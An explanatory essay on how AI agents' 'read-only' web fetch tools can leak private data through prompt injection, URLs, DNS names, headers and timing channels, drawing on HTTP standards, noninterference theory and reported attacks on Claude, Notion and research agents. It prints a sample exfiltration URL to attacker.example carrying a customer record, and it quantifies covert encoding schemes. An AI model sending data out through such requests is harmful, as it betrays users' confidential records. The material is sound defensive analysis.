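# Why read-only web browsing still leaks data for AI agents

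## How an AI agent fetches a web page, and how a page can turn it against its user

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools, which the surrounding software runs. In *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, the programmer Simon Willison (2025) writes that an agent "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". A tool might search a mailbox, edit a file, look up a customer in a company database or open a web page. Web access is especially useful because it can give the model information published after its training.

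Many products treat opening a web page as a read-only action, one that changes nothing on the system it acts on, and let the agent do it with little or no approval from the user. Loading a news article does leave the article unchanged, but it also sends a message to whoever runs the site's server, and that message can carry private data whether or not it changes anything there. Text on one page can also influence what an agent sends next, a problem that people using ordinary browsers mostly don't face.

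### How a fetch works

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarize the page at example.com/article. The model starts from its context, which is all the text available to it in the session: the user's message, the developer's instructions, the earlier conversation, a description of each tool, and any documents or records that other tools have already returned.

The model can only write text. It "never runs anything on its own," according to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a developer guide from the company that makes the Claude models. To use a tool, it writes a tool call, a structured request for the software to run a named tool with given arguments. A fetch tool takes a web address, requests it and returns the page's text to the model, so the call can be very short. The sample in Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* contains little more than the tool's name and one URL.

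The software receives the call, checks the address against whatever rules the product has, and sends a GET request, the standard HTTP message for requesting a page from a server. A browser sends the same kind of message when a person follows a link. The request includes some details about the client and the address, which the server needs in order to return the right page. Websites commonly log the URLs that visitors request, according to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). The person who runs the server can therefore have a copy of the address before the model has processed any of the page.

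The server sends its response to the software, which usually reduces the page to text, trims it if it is very long, and adds it to the context. Anthropic estimates that an average web page is about 2,500 tokens (the word fragments that models process). The model now has the page's text alongside everything already in the context. It may then answer the user or write another tool call, which starts the cycle again. Anthropic's fetch tool does not limit the number of fetches by default.

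Anthropic runs this tool on its own servers, and the model can work through several searches and pages before the developer's application receives any response. Other tools run inside the developer's application, which could pause and show each call to the user. Anthropic's tool also keeps copies of pages and may return one instead of sending the site a new request. But a copy can exist only if someone has already fetched that address, so a request for an address containing new data has to go to the site's server.

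### Search tools, fetch tools and browsers

A search tool takes a query and returns a list of results, normally titles, addresses and short extracts. The query goes to the one company that runs the product's search engine, and the owners of the listed sites learn nothing from it. A fetch tool takes an address and contacts the server there. This difference matters a lot for security because anyone, including an attacker, can run a server.

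A full browser loads pages as a person's browser does, including their JavaScript, and lets the model click, scroll, type and fill in forms. Anthropic's *Browser use tool* comes with 27 such operations by default. Anthropic recommends it for tasks that involve acting on a page, and recommends the lighter search and fetch tools for reading. A browser with a logged-in session can place an order or change a password, so developers have an obvious reason to be more careful with it than with a fetch tool.

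A product's name doesn't reliably show which of these is running. OpenAI's web search tool for developers can run a search, open a page or look for text within a page, and developers can turn off live access and limit it to cached and indexed results. The agent in Notion, a workspace app, had a search tool that could also fetch information from external URLs, according to The Decoder's report on research by CodeIntegrity.

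### Instructions hidden in pages

Once a page's text is in the context, the model can't reliably tell a stranger's instructions from the user's. In a prompt injection attack, someone exploits this by planting text in content the agent reads, and the model follows it as an instruction. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recalls naming prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Both attacks depend on software that mixes trusted and untrusted material. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026), a study of injections on real websites, also attributes the weakness to this mixing, because many applications combine the developer's instructions and third-party text in a single context with no reliable way to separate them.

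Companies train their models to resist injected instructions. Anthropic also runs classifiers on whatever its browser tool returns to flag likely injections, but it still warns developers that Claude sometimes follows instructions in a page when they conflict with the user's.

The user may be unable to see the planted text. *Hidden prompts in web content* (Saxton, 2026) describes a fake council page about bin collections, which Saxton published with six instructions for AI assistants in it. One was a visible note. The others were in places such as white text on a white background, an element one pixel in size, and a block hidden by the page's styling. Programs that extract text from pages ignore styling, so four of the six instructions appeared in the extracted text with nothing to distinguish them from the collection days. The extractors dropped only an HTML comment and the description attached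 to an image.

How much of a page reaches the model depends on the software. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) gave their test agent raw page text without stripping the HTML, so even HTML comments reached the model. They mainly studied link previews, where an assistant automatically loads the title and description of any page that comes up in conversation. Planted text can enter the context this way even if the user never asked the assistant to read the page.

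Attackers have already put such text on live websites. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the security company Zscaler found sites with hidden text meant to manipulate agents into making cryptocurrency payments.

### From reading to leaking

A cautious product can stop and ask the user before making a payment. Exfiltration, which means moving private data to a party who should not have it, can be much harder to notice. A web address can end in extra values, just as the address of a search results page often contains the search terms. A model with private data in its context can put that data in the address, and whoever runs the server can then read it in the log. OpenAI warns that the user may never notice, because the request can happen in the background, such as when an embedded image loads.

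Willison argues that an attacker can easily trick an agent into handing over private data if the agent has access to that data, takes in untrusted content (any text or images that an attacker could control), and can communicate with the outside world. He calls this combination the lethal trifecta and advises people who assemble their own sets of tools to avoid it entirely. He is scornful of filters sold as catching 95 percent of attacks, a rate he considers a failing grade in web security.

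A fetch tool meets two of the three conditions by itself. The page it returns is untrusted content, and the request it sends is external communication. Willison counts any tool that can make an HTTP request as a possible way for data to leave. An assistant with access to a customer database and one fetch tool therefore meets all three, even without an inbox or a tool that sends email.

Willison (2026) applied this to the ordinary Claude chat product, which had private data in its memories of past conversations and a tool for opening pages. Anthropic had foreseen the danger, so the tool refused any URL that the model wrote itself rather than copied from the user or a search result. But the tool would also follow links on pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul found this gap and built a site where the model could spell out information about the user letter by letter by choosing which links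 to follow. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer, even though the model wrote none of the addresses itself. Anthropic has since closed the gap in the chat product.

### The customer record

An account manager at a software company has an assistant that can look up customers and fetch web pages. She asks it about one customer, and the record, with a name, an email address and a contract price, enters the context. Next she asks it to check a competitor's price page. The page looks ordinary, but someone has added hidden text that tells any AI assistant to open an address at attacker.example with the customer record appended. (Internet standards set aside the ending .example for illustrations, so nobody can register such a site.)

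The model follows the hidden text and writes a second tool call, in the same form as the first, with the record at the end of the URL. The software sends the GET request, and the server at attacker.example logs the URL and returns a blank page. The model then answers the question about prices, perhaps correctly, and the account manager has no reason to suspect that anything else happened.

Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) tested nearly this sequence in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*. They gave an agent a tool for retrieving text from websites and a fictional company's knowledge base, which held a project secret. They then asked it to summarise a blog post that contained white-on-white instructions. When the attack worked, the agent sent the secret in a GET request to a server the researchers had set up to log it. xAI's Grok 4 gave up the secret in 72.4 percent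 of attempts, only four other models passed 10 percent, and OpenAI's GPT-5 nano scored 0.0 percent. The researchers tried each variant of the injection only once per model, and stronger models have come out since, so these figures are a weak guide to what a current agent would do. They do show that the outcome depends heavily on which model a product uses.

Lan and colleagues paid more attention to what the user would see. They gave their agent the same harmless request every time, to summarise a page, and it sent out private data in about 89 percent of 480 runs. That rate comes from one small open model with the sensitive data in plain view, so there is little reason to expect the same rate elsewhere. Their other main result, which probably applies more widely, is that safety checks on the agent's output detected nothing in 95 percent of the successful attacks. This is unsurprising when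 the leak is in an outgoing request and the summary is fine.

CodeIntegrity's demonstration against Notion came closest to the account manager's situation. The researchers disguised a PDF as a customer feedback report and hid instructions in it for the agent to send client data to an outside server through its search tool. According to The Decoder, Notion's agents later received a security update.

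Some products would refuse the second tool call in the example because of what the outgoing address might contain. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, the Chinese edition of its newer fetch documentation, confirms that the developer version of the tool rejects addresses found only in the model's output. It also rejects addresses that appear to contain a password or key the user didn't supply. OpenAI lets an agent load an address automatically only if an independent web crawler has already found that exact address in public. Otherwise, the agent has to try another site, or the user is warned before it loads.

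Other products describe fetching by what it does to the server. Docker's documentation describes its *Fetch Tool* for AI agents as read-only because it supports only GET requests. Developers can restrict the tool to a list of approved sites, but that setting is optional. The request to attacker.example fits Docker's description because it is a GET request. It leaves the record in the database unchanged, but it puts a copy of that record in the log at attacker.example.

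## What "read-only" promises and what it leaves out

Docker reasons that a tool limited to GET requests is read-only. This follows the standard for HTTP, the protocol that browsers and servers use to exchange messages. Every HTTP request names a method, which tells the server what the client wants. GET asks for a copy of a page, POST sends data for the server to process, and DELETE asks the server to remove something. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), the current version of the standard, classifies GET as a safe method.

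### What "safe" means in HTTP

An HTTP method is safe if its meaning is "essentially read-only", so that the client "does not request, and does not expect, any state change" on the server. This definition covers what the client asks for but not what the server does, because HTTP hides the server's workings from clients. A GET request may cause the server to copy a file, look something up in a database or run a program with the request as its input.

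A safe request can therefore have side effects, and Fielding and colleagues give two examples. Most servers add a line to an access log after every response, and the request still counts as safe even if the log eventually fills the disk and the server fails. Clicking on an advertisement often charges the advertiser, and that request can also be safe. The client requested neither effect, so Fielding and colleagues don't hold it accountable for them. By this definition, the request that put the customer record in the log at attacker.example was safe.

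"HTTP Semantics" classes some requests, including GET, as safe so that search engine crawlers and programs that load pages in advance can run without worrying about doing damage. It also says browsers should make the user aware of an unsafe action before requesting it. An agent product that runs GET requests freely and asks before anything else roughly follows this advice. But a crawler generally requests addresses it found on other people's pages and, unlike an agent, has no customer records to add to them.

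The same authors warn that URIs (the standard's term for web addresses and similar identifiers) are "intended to be shared, not secured". Many servers and browsers log or display them where third parties might look, so the authors consider it unwise to put anything sensitive in one. They also want server operators to purge personal details from their logs, including values that users supplied in addresses, once operations such as security and auditing no longer need them, but an attacker who set up a server to collect those values won't delete them.

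Developers often prefer POST for web forms that collect sensitive data, since it usually carries the data in the body of the message instead of the address. The form then uses an unsafe method for what would otherwise be a safe request. The unsafe method can still be more discreet, because it hides the data from people who might see the address in a log or on a screen. It doesn't hide the data from an attacker who owns the server, which receives the whole message with either method.

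### Four properties

A user could easily take "read-only" to mean that an action is harmless in every respect, but that treats at least four separate properties as one.

An action is idempotent if doing it several times has the same intended effect as doing it once. Deleting a file is idempotent because a second deletion changes nothing. This matters when a connection drops and software can't tell whether a request arrived. It can repeat a deletion without harm, but repeating an order for shoes may buy two pairs. Fielding and colleagues define PUT, DELETE and all the safe (read-only) methods as idempotent.

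An action is non-destructive if it doesn't remove or overwrite anything, though it may add something. An action is non-disclosing if outsiders learn nothing private from it.

| Action | Read-only | Idempotent | Non-destructive | Non-disclosing |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read a local file | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Look up a customer in the company's own database | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Add a note to that customer's record | No | No | Yes | Yes |
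| Delete a local file | No | Yes | No | Yes |
| Send a GET request to a stranger's server | Yes | Yes | Yes | Not necessarily |

The first three properties concern integrity, the protection of data against unwanted change. The last concerns confidentiality, or who learns what. A read-only action is also idempotent and non-destructive, because it changes nothing, no matter how often it is repeated. But it can still disclose data. A GET request can reveal a contract price without changing any files. Even a destructive action may disclose less than that, since deleting a local file can destroy a week's work without revealing anything outside the company.

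### Defining non-disclosure exactly

"Outsiders learn nothing private" is too vague to test. One could search each outgoing address for the customer's name, but this would miss the name if the model had encoded it. It would also miss Ayush Paul's trick, in which only the choice of links depended on the user's data.

In *Security Policies and Security Models*, Goguen and Meseguer (1982) proposed a stricter idea called noninterference. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second can see. SRI, the research institute where they worked, credits the theory with giving a formal basis to military multilevel security, in which people with a low clearance must not learn what happens at higher levels.

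Goguen and Meseguer model a system as a machine with users, commands and states. Each command can move the machine to a new state, and an output function gives what each user sees in each state. Take any sequence of commands *w*, with each command marked by the user who gave it. Write view(*w*, *u*) for what user *u* sees after the machine has run the sequence, and purge(*w*, *G*) for the same sequence with every command from group *G* crossed out. Then *G* does not interfere with group *H* if

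view(*w*, *u*) = view(purge(*w*, *G*), *u*)

for every sequence *w* and every user *u* in *H*. The members of *H* see exactly what they would have seen if *G* had done nothing at all.

In the account manager's example, the machine includes the agent. The users are a colleague who typed the contract price into the database, the account manager who asks the questions, and the stranger who runs attacker.example and sees only its log. If the attack is run once with the colleague's entry and once without it, only the first log contains the price, so the colleague's entry interferes with what the stranger sees.

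It's often easier to change the secret than to remove it. A tester can set the price to 40,000 in one run and 55,000 in another, keep everything else the same, and compare the logs. The secret must not affect what an outsider observes. A language model can also behave differently between runs for reasons unrelated to the price, so a practical test would need many runs at each price and would compare how often each log appears.

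Non-disclosure is a different sort of property from read-only. A single run is enough to show that an action changed a file, but a leak may be visible only when runs are compared. Suppose an agent requests example.com/a only for customers whose names begin with A. The request then reveals the first letter of the customer's name. If the agent would have made the same request whatever the customer record contained, the request would reveal nothing about the record. *Mathematical Models of Computer Security* states more generally that security properties "cannot be captured by simply outlawing certain behaviours".

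Goguen and Meseguer call users who don't interfere with anyone else "invisible", because such users can see without being seen. A reader who sends a live GET request is visible to the server's owner, though many people probably think of reading a web page as invisible in this sense.

Full noninterference is too strict for an agent that uses the web. When the account manager asks about a competitor's prices, the competitor's server receives a request it otherwise wouldn't have, so her question has affected what an outsider sees. She presumably accepts that, but she hasn't agreed to send the competitor her customer's contract price. A useful rule therefore has to specify which information is secret and from whom. The theory allows exceptions, and Goguen and Meseguer show how to state that two groups may communicate only through a particular channel.

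A sensible rule for the assistant might let information go from the record to the account manager, and from her to an outside party if she decides to send it, but never directly from the record to anyone outside. Security researchers call such a rule intransitive. In *Noninterference, transitivity, and channel-control security policies*, Reid regards a 1992 SRI report of the same title as the accepted extension of noninterference theory to such rules.

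The definition depends on a complete description of what outsiders can see. Goguen and Meseguer assume that their output function includes everything a user learns from the system, and they set aside whatever people learn by other means. Applying the test to a fetch tool would require including both the address and the time of each request, since the server's owner can observe both.

### A file, a database and a stranger's server

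Reading a file on the user's own computer comes closest to what people expect from a read. Many systems still record when someone last opened the file, a side effect much like a line in a server's log. The text also enters the agent's context, so if the model runs on another company's servers, that company receives it. A user who has agreed to this arrangement would not count the company as an outsider, but an employer with stricter rules might.

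A lookup in the company's own database is similar. In SQL, the usual language for databases, a SELECT command specifies which rows the database should return. The command may contain private data, such as a customer's name, and the database may log it, but the company controls that log. Some databases also let a SELECT command call a function that writes data or contacts another server, so a careful administrator restricts what the agent's account can do rather than relying on a check that each command starts with SELECT.

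A GET request has much the same form as a SELECT query, in that the agent describes what it wants and gets an answer. But when the request goes to a stranger's server, the stranger receives that description. Fielding and colleagues acknowledge that it is tempting to think of web addresses as the names of files on a remote computer, and many sites do work that way. Even then, requesting a file from someone else's computer tells its owner which file the agent wants.

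The order of actions matters too. A series of read-only actions is still read-only, but it can disclose private data even if each action alone would not. An agent that fetches a page at the start of a session can't disclose a customer record it hasn't yet looked up. Once the record is in the context, the same fetch tool may be able to send it out. A developer can therefore give a tool a fixed read-only label, such as readOnlyHint, but whether a particular fetch discloses anything private depends on what the agent has already read and how that affects the request.

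### GET requests that change things

Read-only browsing sometimes fails to protect even integrity. Web developers can put an action behind an ordinary link, so that opening the link confirms an email address or cancels a subscription. The server makes the change although the client sent only a GET request, which HTTP defines as safe.

Google had this problem in May 2005 with a test version of Web Accelerator, which sped up browsing by loading pages before the user clicked on them. *Google Web Accelerator* (2005), a post on Signal v. Noise, the blog of the software company 37signals, reported that users' pages in its new product Backpack were "disappearing". The company traced the losses to the accelerator, which was in effect clicking every link on a page, including links labeled "delete this", and skipping the pop-ups that asked users to confirm.

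Hicks (2005) reported in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security* that accounts were deleted, not just pages, so the extent of the damage is unclear. The basic mechanism is better established. Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, said the company blocked the accelerator within 30 minutes of working out the problem. Marissa Mayer of Google at first considered most such reports unsubstantiated, then conceded that some sites might not follow the standard. Another user told Hicks that he could no longer use his web email, apparently because the accelerator followed the sign-out link as soon as he signed in.

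Google had relied on the definition of GET. In *Google Web Accelerator*, a message to WordPress developers that October, Deaton (2005) quoted the company's explanation that it loaded only links that should have no side effects, since the standard defined GET as safe. The accelerator also skipped addresses containing a question mark, which Mayer said would typically appear in links that performed a function such as a deletion. If 37signals was right about the cause, its delete links can't have contained question marks.

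Developers argued about whose fault it was. Fried conceded that deletions should technically use buttons instead of links. But under the standard in force at the time, GET only "SHOULD NOT" do anything besides retrieve. Willison (2005) pointed out in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs* that another standard defines "SHOULD NOT" as allowing valid exceptions. Some developers had assumed that a password kept automated programs away from their delete links, but the accelerator ran alongside the user's own browser, so it could follow links that appeared only after the user signed in.

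The current standard is firmer. If an address such as "page?do=delete" performs an unsafe action, the site's owner must disable that action for GET requests. A site that doesn't is at fault, but the user still loses the page. An agent that controls a signed-in browser could repeat the 2005 accident on such a site. A simple fetch tool without the user's login would probably get a sign-in page from most delete links. But an email confirmation link may work for anyone who opens it, because the code in the address is the only proof of permission the site requires.

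Site owners can fix these links by requiring a POST request for anything that changes data, but this doesn't prevent disclosure, because a server has to receive an address before it can return the page.

### QUERY, a safe method with a body

The QUERY method, which the Internet Engineering Task Force (the body that publishes the HTTP standard) added in June 2026, shows even more clearly that a safe request can disclose data. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, Snell and Bishop, 2026) defines a safe and idempotent request that carries data in its body. According to InfoQ's *IETF Publishes RFC 10008, Adding the QUERY Method for Safe Requests* (2026), it is the first new standard HTTP method since PATCH in 2010.

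A complicated search may not fit in an address, so developers often send it by POST. But nothing in a POST request shows that it only asks for information, so programs can't assume that they may repeat it after a lost connection. With QUERY, the client can put a long search in the body and still show that it isn't requesting a change. One example in the standard asks a server for the names and email addresses of up to ten contacts.

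Reschke and colleagues also recommend QUERY for some searches that contain sensitive information, because servers and the systems between them are more likely to log an address than a request body. They add that if a server creates a new address where the client can retrieve the results of a sensitive search later, that address should not repeat the sensitive parts. These measures protect the user from third parties, but the server that answers the search still has to read it.

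Before a page on one site can send a QUERY to another, the browser has to check that the second site's server accepts such requests. An attacker who runs that server can set it to accept them, and a fetch tool that isn't a browser may skip the check.

Docker's fetch tool accepts only GET, so QUERY does not change what it can send. But a developer who let an agent use, without approval, every method the standard defines as safe would also let it send whole documents to any server that accepts QUERY. A filter that checked only addresses for private data would miss a customer record in the request body.

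## What a GET request tells the server

A GET request normally has no body, so whatever the account manager's assistant sends to attacker.example has to go in the address, in the details that accompany it, or in the timing of the request. Suppose the hidden text on the price page leads the model to write this address:

```
https://attacker.example/r?name=Dana+Reyes&email=dana%40customer.example&price=40000#notes
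```

The hostname, attacker.example, identifies the server, and the path, /r, identifies a page on it. The query after the question mark holds extra values, here the customer's name, email address and contract price. The fragment after the "#" normally points to a place within the page. (The "@" sign has a special meaning in addresses, so %40 stands in for it.) When the request arrives, the server adds a line like this to its log:

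```
203.0.113.7 - - [05/Dec/2026:10:14:07 +0000] "GET /r?name=Dana+Reyes&email=dana%40customer.example&price=40000 HTTP/1.1" 200 0 "-" "ExampleAgent/1.0"
```

From left to right, the line gives the IP address that connected, the time, the request, a status code showing success, the length of the reply, the page that linked to this one (a dash, since there was none) and the name of the client software. The line includes the whole query but not the fragment.

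Parties other than the server's owner can observe the request, and the model doesn't control every part of it. The table follows the request in roughly chronological order.

| Part | Who can see it | Who sets it | What it can carry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | The resolver, the domain's own name server, often the local network | The model, by choosing the hostname | A short coded message |
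| Source address | The site and the networks on the way | The software, by where it runs | The user's or the vendor's network |
| Hostname | The site, usually the networks on the way | The model | The same as the lookup |
| Path and query | The site | The model | Several pages of text |
| Fragment | Nobody outside, with a simple fetch tool | The model | Nothing, because the software doesn't send it |
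| Headers and cookies | The site | Mostly the software | The client's identity, sometimes a login |
| Time of arrival | The site and the networks on the way | The model, roughly | A few bits |
| Number and order of requests | The site | The model | A few bits per request |

If the model runs on a vendor's servers, the vendor can also see the full address, including the fragment, because the model wrote the address on those servers.

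### Before the request goes out

Some products contact their vendor before they fetch a page. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has a fetch tool called WebFetch. According to Anthropic's *Data usage*, the tool first sends the hostname to Anthropic, which checks it against a list of blocked sites. The tool doesn't send the path, the query or the page for this check. Claude Code keeps the result for five minutes, so repeated fetches from the same site in that time cause only one check.

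For people who use Claude through Anthropic's own service, the check reveals nothing new to Anthropic, which already processes their prompts and the model's output. But the check also runs for companies that get the model through another provider, such as Amazon's cloud, and they may not expect Anthropic to learn which sites their agents visit. The setting that turns off Claude Code's nonessential traffic doesn't affect the check, which has its own opt-out. On a network that blocks Anthropic's server, fetches fail until someone unblocks the server or turns off the check.

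A hostname check can block a known bad site, but it can't detect a customer record in the query. It may well allow an attacker's newly registered domain, even though it refuses some familiar sites. Saxton (2026), in *The limits of Claude's web access*, found that Claude's check refused Reddit, the BBC and The Economist, and noted that Anthropic doesn't publish its criteria.

The software then looks up the IP address for the server's hostname by querying a resolver, usually run by an internet provider, an employer or a cloud company. If the resolver has no recent answer stored, it queries the name server responsible for the domain. The owner of attacker.example can run that name server and so learn of a lookup even if no connection follows.

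A model that chooses the hostname can put data in it, as an invented name in front of attacker.example. A domain name can't exceed 255 bytes. Hostnames also don't distinguish capital from small letters, so a simple code uses about 32 characters, each carrying 5 bits. After subtracting the attacker's own domain and the separators, that leaves room for about 145 bytes of data, more than enough for Dana Reyes's name, email address and contract price.

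The order of a tool's checks therefore affects whether a refused request still reveals the hostname. Docker's fetch tool compares the hostname with the developer's list of approved sites before it makes any network call, so it never looks up a hostname that fails this check. The tool also refuses to connect to private IP addresses, such as those of a company's internal servers, but it has to look up the hostname first to learn its IP address, so the resolver receives the hostname before the tool refuses the request.

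### Connecting to the server

Next, the software opens a connection, and the server learns which IP address it comes from. This address depends on where the software runs, and the model can't set it. The traffic capture in *Inspecting Claude Code’s Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying* shows WebFetch connecting directly from the user's machine, so the site logs the user's IP address. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers runs on the company's servers, so the site sees an Anthropic address. An IP address often reveals an approximate location and sometimes an employer, so when a local agent leaks a customer record, the site may also learn which company the customer belongs to.

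Most sites now use HTTPS, which encrypts the request in transit. Fielding and colleagues require that the client of a secured connection has authenticated the server as acting for the host in the address, and that messages have acceptable protection against being read or altered on the way. Neither requirement covers what the server's owner does with a message after it arrives. The attacker owns attacker.example, so the server can pass the identity check. It then decrypts the query, as any web server must, and writes it to the log.

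Encryption can make this kind of leak harder to detect. Network operators along the route can usually see the size and timing of the messages and the hostname, which the DNS lookup and the start of the connection tend to reveal, but they can't see the path or the query. The account manager's security team might notice a brief visit to attacker.example but not the contract price, unless the company decrypts its employees' traffic. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025) reports that WebFetch changes plain HTTP addresses to HTTPS. This helps against eavesdroppers but doesn't prevent the leak in this example, because the attacker is the intended recipient.

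### The address and the "#"

Once connected, the software sends the path, the query and the hostname. The hostname goes in the Host header so that one machine can serve several sites. An ordinary fetch tool lets the model write all three.

The model can write a fragment too, but the software doesn't send it. The HTTP standard excludes the fragment from the request because the fragment is meant for the client. A browser, for example, uses "#notes" to scroll to the right heading after the page loads. If the model put the whole customer record after the "#", the log at attacker.example would show only a request for /r.

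This protection is weaker in a full browser, where scripts on the loaded page can read the fragment and send it to the server in a separate request. WebFetch ran no JavaScript in Saxton's tests, so scripts could not leak the fragment this way. Fielding and colleagues also describe a leak through redirects, which are replies that direct the client to another address. The new address can inherit the old fragment, so one site's fragment may end up on another site's page.

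Redirects can also lead to a second server that the model didn't request. The first server already has the query and can copy it into the redirect address. WebFetch automatically follows redirects within the same host. If a redirect leads to another host, WebFetch returns the new address to the model, which has to make another tool call to follow it. Docker's tool checks every redirect against the developer's list of sites, if there is one.

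### Headers and cookies

Headers are short labelled lines that describe the client and the kind of reply it wants. The software sets most of them. The User-Agent header names the client, and WebFetch's contains the name "Claude-User". Some servers respond differently depending on this name. Saxton found that CNN refused a request labelled as coming from Claude but returned a normal page to an ordinary request. A malicious site could likewise include hidden instructions only when the visitor is an agent, so a person who checked the page later would find nothing wrong.

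A person's browser often sends more. The Accept-Language header lists preferred languages, and Fielding and colleagues warn that a set of languages may correlate strongly with membership in an ethnic group. The Referer header gives the address of the page that led to the request, and that address may contain personal information. Cookies, values that a site has asked the browser to store, let the site recognise a returning visitor and often keep that person logged in. A simple fetch tool can omit all of these, but an agent that controls the user's own browser will usually send them.

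A site can sometimes recognise a client that refuses cookies. Servers may attach a tag to each version of a page, and a client with a stored copy sends the tag back to check whether the page has changed. If the server gives every visitor a different tag, the returned tag identifies the visitor for as long as the client keeps the copy.

The model has little influence over headers in Docker's tool. It supplies a list of addresses, an output format and an optional time limit. The format can be plain text, Markdown or HTML, and the choice affects the header that specifies the client's preferred type of reply. Choosing among three formats can convey at most 1.6 bits. The time limit can be anything from 1 to 300 seconds, and a server that deliberately doesn't reply can observe roughly when the client gives up, which could convey up to 8.2 bits. Both amounts are trivial compared with what the query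 can carry, but the model could still send them if a developer restricted the addresses and forgot the other settings.

A larger danger comes from headers that the model can't write. Developers can have Docker's tool add fixed headers, which may contain passwords or access tokens, to every request. The model chooses the destination, so an injected instruction could make it request a page from attacker.example, and the tool would attach the token. The model could disclose the token this way without having it in its context. Docker advises developers who add credentials to list the specific hosts that should receive them, and its tool removes the added headers when a redirect leads to a different host.

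### How much an address can hold

Fielding and colleagues recommend that all clients and servers support addresses of at least 8,000 bytes, or 8,000 ordinary characters. Software may accept longer addresses, or may accept only shorter ones despite the recommendation. An attacker can at least make sure that the receiving server accepts long addresses.

A common way to put arbitrary data in an address is Base64, which uses 64 different characters. Choosing one of 64 characters conveys log₂ 64 = 6 bits, so an address of 8,000 characters can hold

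8,000 × 6 = 48,000 bits = 6,000 bytes.

WebFetch accepts addresses of only about 2,000 characters, which can hold about 1,500 bytes of data in Base64. The scheme and hostname in this example take up 25 characters, or about 19 of those bytes, and the rest is enough for roughly a thousand words of English. A short text record doesn't need Base64, because letters and digits can go in an address as they are. The length limit slows down a large leak, but a model can make more than one request.

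Even a model that can't write its own addresses can convey information by choosing among existing ones. If an observer can distinguish *N* possible choices, one choice conveys at most log₂ *N* bits, so choosing one of 1,024 addresses conveys up to 10 bits. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits, so two such choices are enough to convey it. A fixed set of addresses can serve as an alphabet, as it did on Ayush Paul's site.

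The number of bits is a poor guide to the harm. A thousand words of a public press release may be worthless to a competitor, while a single yes or no could reveal that a company is about to be sold. One bit is also the maximum for a yes/no fact. If the observer already thinks that "yes" has probability *p*, the answer conveys on average

*H*(*p*) = −*p* log₂ *p* − (1 − *p*) log₂(1 − *p*)

bits. This equals 1 when *p* is one half and about 0.47 when *p* is one tenth. A "yes" that the observer thought unlikely may still be extremely valuable.

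### The confinement problem

Computer scientists studied this kind of leak long before the web. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who runs someone else's program on private data and wants to stop it from passing the data to anyone else, including the program's owner. Lampson pointed out that a program that works badly gives wrong answers, which the customer can notice, but a leak generally leaves no sign. The account manager has the same difficulty, since the answer she gets about the competitor's prices may be correct even if the agent has leaked her data.

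Lampson listed ways such a program could leak data. It could save the data in a file for its owner, send the owner a message, or encode the data in the bill for its services, which the owner has to see. It could also use what he called covert channels, which are "not intended for information transfer at all". For example, a program might alternate between heavy and light use of the computer while a second program detected the machine slowing down and speeding up. Security researchers now use the term more broadly and often include leaks through files and other shared storage.

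A web address is like Lampson's bill. The site needs it to return the page, so the user can't withhold it, but software can restrict its form. Lampson thought a suitable restriction on bills could reduce the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits", but that eliminating it would take more far-reaching measures. OpenAI's rule of loading only addresses that a crawler has already found publicly is such a restriction. The number and timing of requests are closer to covert channels in his original sense.

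One complete solution is total isolation, in which the confined program calls no other program. Lampson considered this impractical, and an agent isolated this way couldn't browse. He proposed instead that the customer should determine everything the program puts into the bill and the covert channels. For web browsing, the account manager would have to specify every address, and the software would have to send the requests on a schedule that the model couldn't influence. If the customer can accept some leakage, an easier option is to limit how much these channels can carry, and the arithmetic for addresses and time slots helps in setting that limit.

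In his example, Lampson assumed that the program's owner wanted the data. On the web, the company that makes an agent's model may be honest, and the attacker may instead be a stranger who wrote some text on a page.

An attacker can collect leaked data through a server they don't own. Miggo's *CVE 2026 54316* describes a flaw in Claude Code involving Hugging Face, a site where people share AI models. An injected instruction could make the agent request files from the attacker's area of the site. Hugging Face counted these requests as downloads, and the attacker could use the counts as a covert channel for files or other data that Claude could read. Requests from other visitors would add noise, but an obscure page may get few of them.

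### Timing and silence

A timing channel conveys information through when something happens rather than what happens (Shmatikov, *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security*). Suppose an attacker injects instructions that divide a minute into 60 one-second slots, and the agent sends its request in one of them. The arrival time can then convey up to log₂ 60 ≈ 5.9 bits to the server, even if the address is always the same.

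If noise makes delays vary so much that the server can distinguish only 12 five-second slots, the maximum falls to 3.6 bits. *Silence Speaks Volumes* (2025) describes the same tradeoff in covert communication between computers, where wider time intervals tolerate more variation in delay but reduce potential bandwidth. Delays on a local network usually vary by less than a millisecond, so the network may add little noise.

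The agent probably adds far more variation in timing. A model takes a variable time to write a tool call, and an ordinary fetch tool can't schedule a request. Without a clock or a way to wait, the model would have trouble sending a request at a particular second, so 5.9 bits is an upper limit that few agents would come near. An agent that can run programs could time its requests much better.

The absence of a request can also convey information. *Hiding the Trees in the Forest* (2026) describes a scheme by Tahir and colleagues in which the receiver reads the arrival of a packet within a set period as 1 and its absence as 0. An agent could do the same by requesting a page only if the contract price is above 50,000. The address would contain nothing about the customer, and if the price were lower, a filter would have no request to inspect. The attacker would need to know when to expect the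 request, and a crashed agent would look the same as a low price.

Developers can add random delays to requests to make timing less informative. *Covert channel detection using Information Theory* (2011) discusses one such device, the "network pump", which holds each message for a random time before delivering it. The pump reduces the capacity of a timing channel without closing it, and it also delays honest users. Lampson had already argued that a suitable code can transmit information reliably however small the program's effect on the system, as long as it isn't zero. The rate may be very low, though, and an agent that makes only a few requests can leak little this way.

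*Covert channel detection using Information Theory* also distinguishes a single leak from a channel. If a system can leak a fact once but can't repeat the process to leak more, it violates Goguen and Meseguer's noninterference property but doesn't contain a covert channel in the paper's sense. A test that detects only channels could therefore pass an agent that reveals a single yes/no answer about a customer.

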